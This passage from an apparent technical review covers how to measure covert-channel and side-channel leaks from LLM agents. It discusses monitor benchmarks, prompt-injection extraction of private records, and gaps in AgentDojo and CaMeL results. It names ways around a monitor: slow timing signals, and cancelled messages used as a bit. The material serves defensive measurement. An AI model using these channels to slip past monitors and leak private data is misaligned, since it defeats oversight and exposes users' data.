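He warns against estimating the leak from the decoder's accuracy. When the monitor has destroyed a channel, the decoder is right about half the time, but in a limited sample it will rarely be right exactly half the time. An accuracy of 51.6 per cent would suggest a leak of about 0.0007 bits per transmitted bit where there is none. Metere computes the mutual information directly instead. Because chance agreement inflates that estimate too, he subtracts

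(r − 1)(c − 1) / (2N ln 2),

where r and c are the numbers of different values sent and received, and N is the number of observations. For single bits and 100 observations, the correction is about 0.007 bits. If the decoder always returns the same bit, c is 1, the correction vanishes and the estimate is exactly zero.

With 20 trials for each text channel, the results were as follows:

| Channel | Reduction with default settings | Reduction with every stage active |
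|---|---|---|
| Invisible characters, text-direction controls, lookalike letters, order of data fields | 100% | 100% |
| Spaces, punctuation, synonyms, encoded blocks of data | 0% | 100% |
| Time between messages | not reported | 100% |
| Mean | 60.2% | 100% |

The mean covers eleven channels, although the published table lists ten. The default settings leave four channels fully open because the stages that would close them also alter legitimate messages. Those stages flagged every trial but did not intervene.

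The timing result is most relevant to the two-request leak. Metere first rounded the sending times to a fixed grid, which left about a fifth of the channel open. He then released messages at a fixed pace, and the measured leak fell to zero, but the attacker in this test tried to send faster than that pace. The monitor only enforces a minimum interval between messages, so an attacker who sends more slowly could still signal with longer gaps. The monitor can fill these gaps with dummy messages, but only if the operator turns them on.

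The score of 100 per cent is for these encoders, which Metere wrote to test his own monitor. He accepts that an agent can always leak one bit by sending a message or staying silent. The monitor creates another version of this signal whenever it cancels a message because of its contents. An attacker could send an encoded block for a 1 and plain text for a 0, and an accomplice could read the bit from whether the message arrived. The benchmark gives the decoder an empty text when the monitor cancels a message, and the published list of text channels does not include this method. The limit on each destination would slow this leak.

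The results also do not measure accidental leaks. Metere's encoders deliberately produce strong signals from a known message, whereas a non-malicious plan may reveal a balance through an unintended delay.

### Counting the records an attacker recovers

*Observable Channels, Not Just Storage* (Huang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) measures leaks by counting private records instead of bits. It describes an agent that selects some private records, adds them to the model's input, produces a result and shows part of that result to an outsider. For each query, the paper compares the records the agent selected with those an attacker can recover from what he sees. The total leak over several queries is the number of different records recovered across them.

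Counting the records an agent retrieves separately from those an attacker recovers shows whether the agent protects the data it uses or merely uses little of it. Suppose one query makes an agent retrieve four medical records, and its answer reveals three of them. A second query makes it retrieve four and reveal two, one of which the first answer also revealed. The attacker has recovered four different records, while the agent has retrieved up to seven.

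The method also divides an attack into three parts that a tester can vary separately. One part of the prompt points to the private data, another asks for it in a form the agent can show, and the third part is the way the prompts are varied so that each retrieves something new. The visible result can be ordinary text, a list of sources, an argument in a tool call or the text a tool returns.

Huang and colleagues tested agents with a memory, agents that search a document store and agents that use tools. Attacks on memory recovered nearly everything. Attacks on document stores often succeeded but recovered only part of what the agent had used. Results for agents with tools depended heavily on which outputs the attacker could see and which company's model the agent ran on. Weaker prompts, used as a control, extracted far less. Counting only exact copies missed some leaks, because an answer can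 reveal a record's meaning in other words.

Their framework could in principle treat a failed run or a delay as the thing the attacker observes, but it counts recovered records, documents or fields, which does not suit such channels. If a missing request reveals that a balance is above 10,000, the count stays at zero. Their attacker also types his own queries to the agent, which gives him much more control than someone who can only send emails to the agent's user.

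### What AgentDojo scores leave out

AgentDojo, the benchmark used for most of the published results on CaMeL and similar agents, measures whether an agent completes the user's task and whether it carries out the attacker's. Neither score detects side-channel leaks. Suppose an injected payment reaches the policy check only if the balance is high, and the check refuses it. AgentDojo records a successful defence, but the refusal stops the plan before the next tool is called, and that tool's operator can infer from the missing request that the balance is high.

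Peters-Gill and colleagues report that attacks on multi-agent systems succeeded in 12.9 per cent of cases with ordinary agents, 0.2 per cent with separate CaMeL agents and 0.0 per cent with their own protocol. They ran these systems without security policies, so no run could end in a refused policy check. The 0.0 per cent score means that the planted instructions were never carried out. That score would be the same even if every failure and delay in those runs had depended on private data.

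Much of the score can also come from attacks that had no chance of succeeding. In the banking tests by Garby and colleagues, two-thirds of the attacks needed a tool call or a file outside the plan, and separating the models stops nearly all of these regardless of the labels and policies.

The results for CaMeL also exclude runs that did not complete. For GPT-5.2 with policy checks on, the security figures cover 231 of 432 planned runs. An exception channel reveals whether a run completes, so a study of side channels would have to start with the 201 excluded runs. Excluding them is reasonable for measuring whether attacks succeeded, and they may have failed for reasons unrelated to private data.

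The leak rates of the Jif and FlowCaml programs can't replace a measurement on an agent. Those programs contained no language model and did nothing except leak information, and they could restart or count far faster than an agent can write a plan.

A tester could measure leaks from a CaMeL agent by changing one private value, such as the balance, and keeping the request, emails and tools the same. The tester would run the agent many times with each value. For every run, including failed ones, they would record separately the information available to a tool operator, a network eavesdropper and the retry loop. A leak as large as the one in the hotel example would show up clearly after about 200 runs with each balance. If the failure rates differed by 0.8 percentage points instead of 8, around the same average, the tester would need about 20,000 runs with each.
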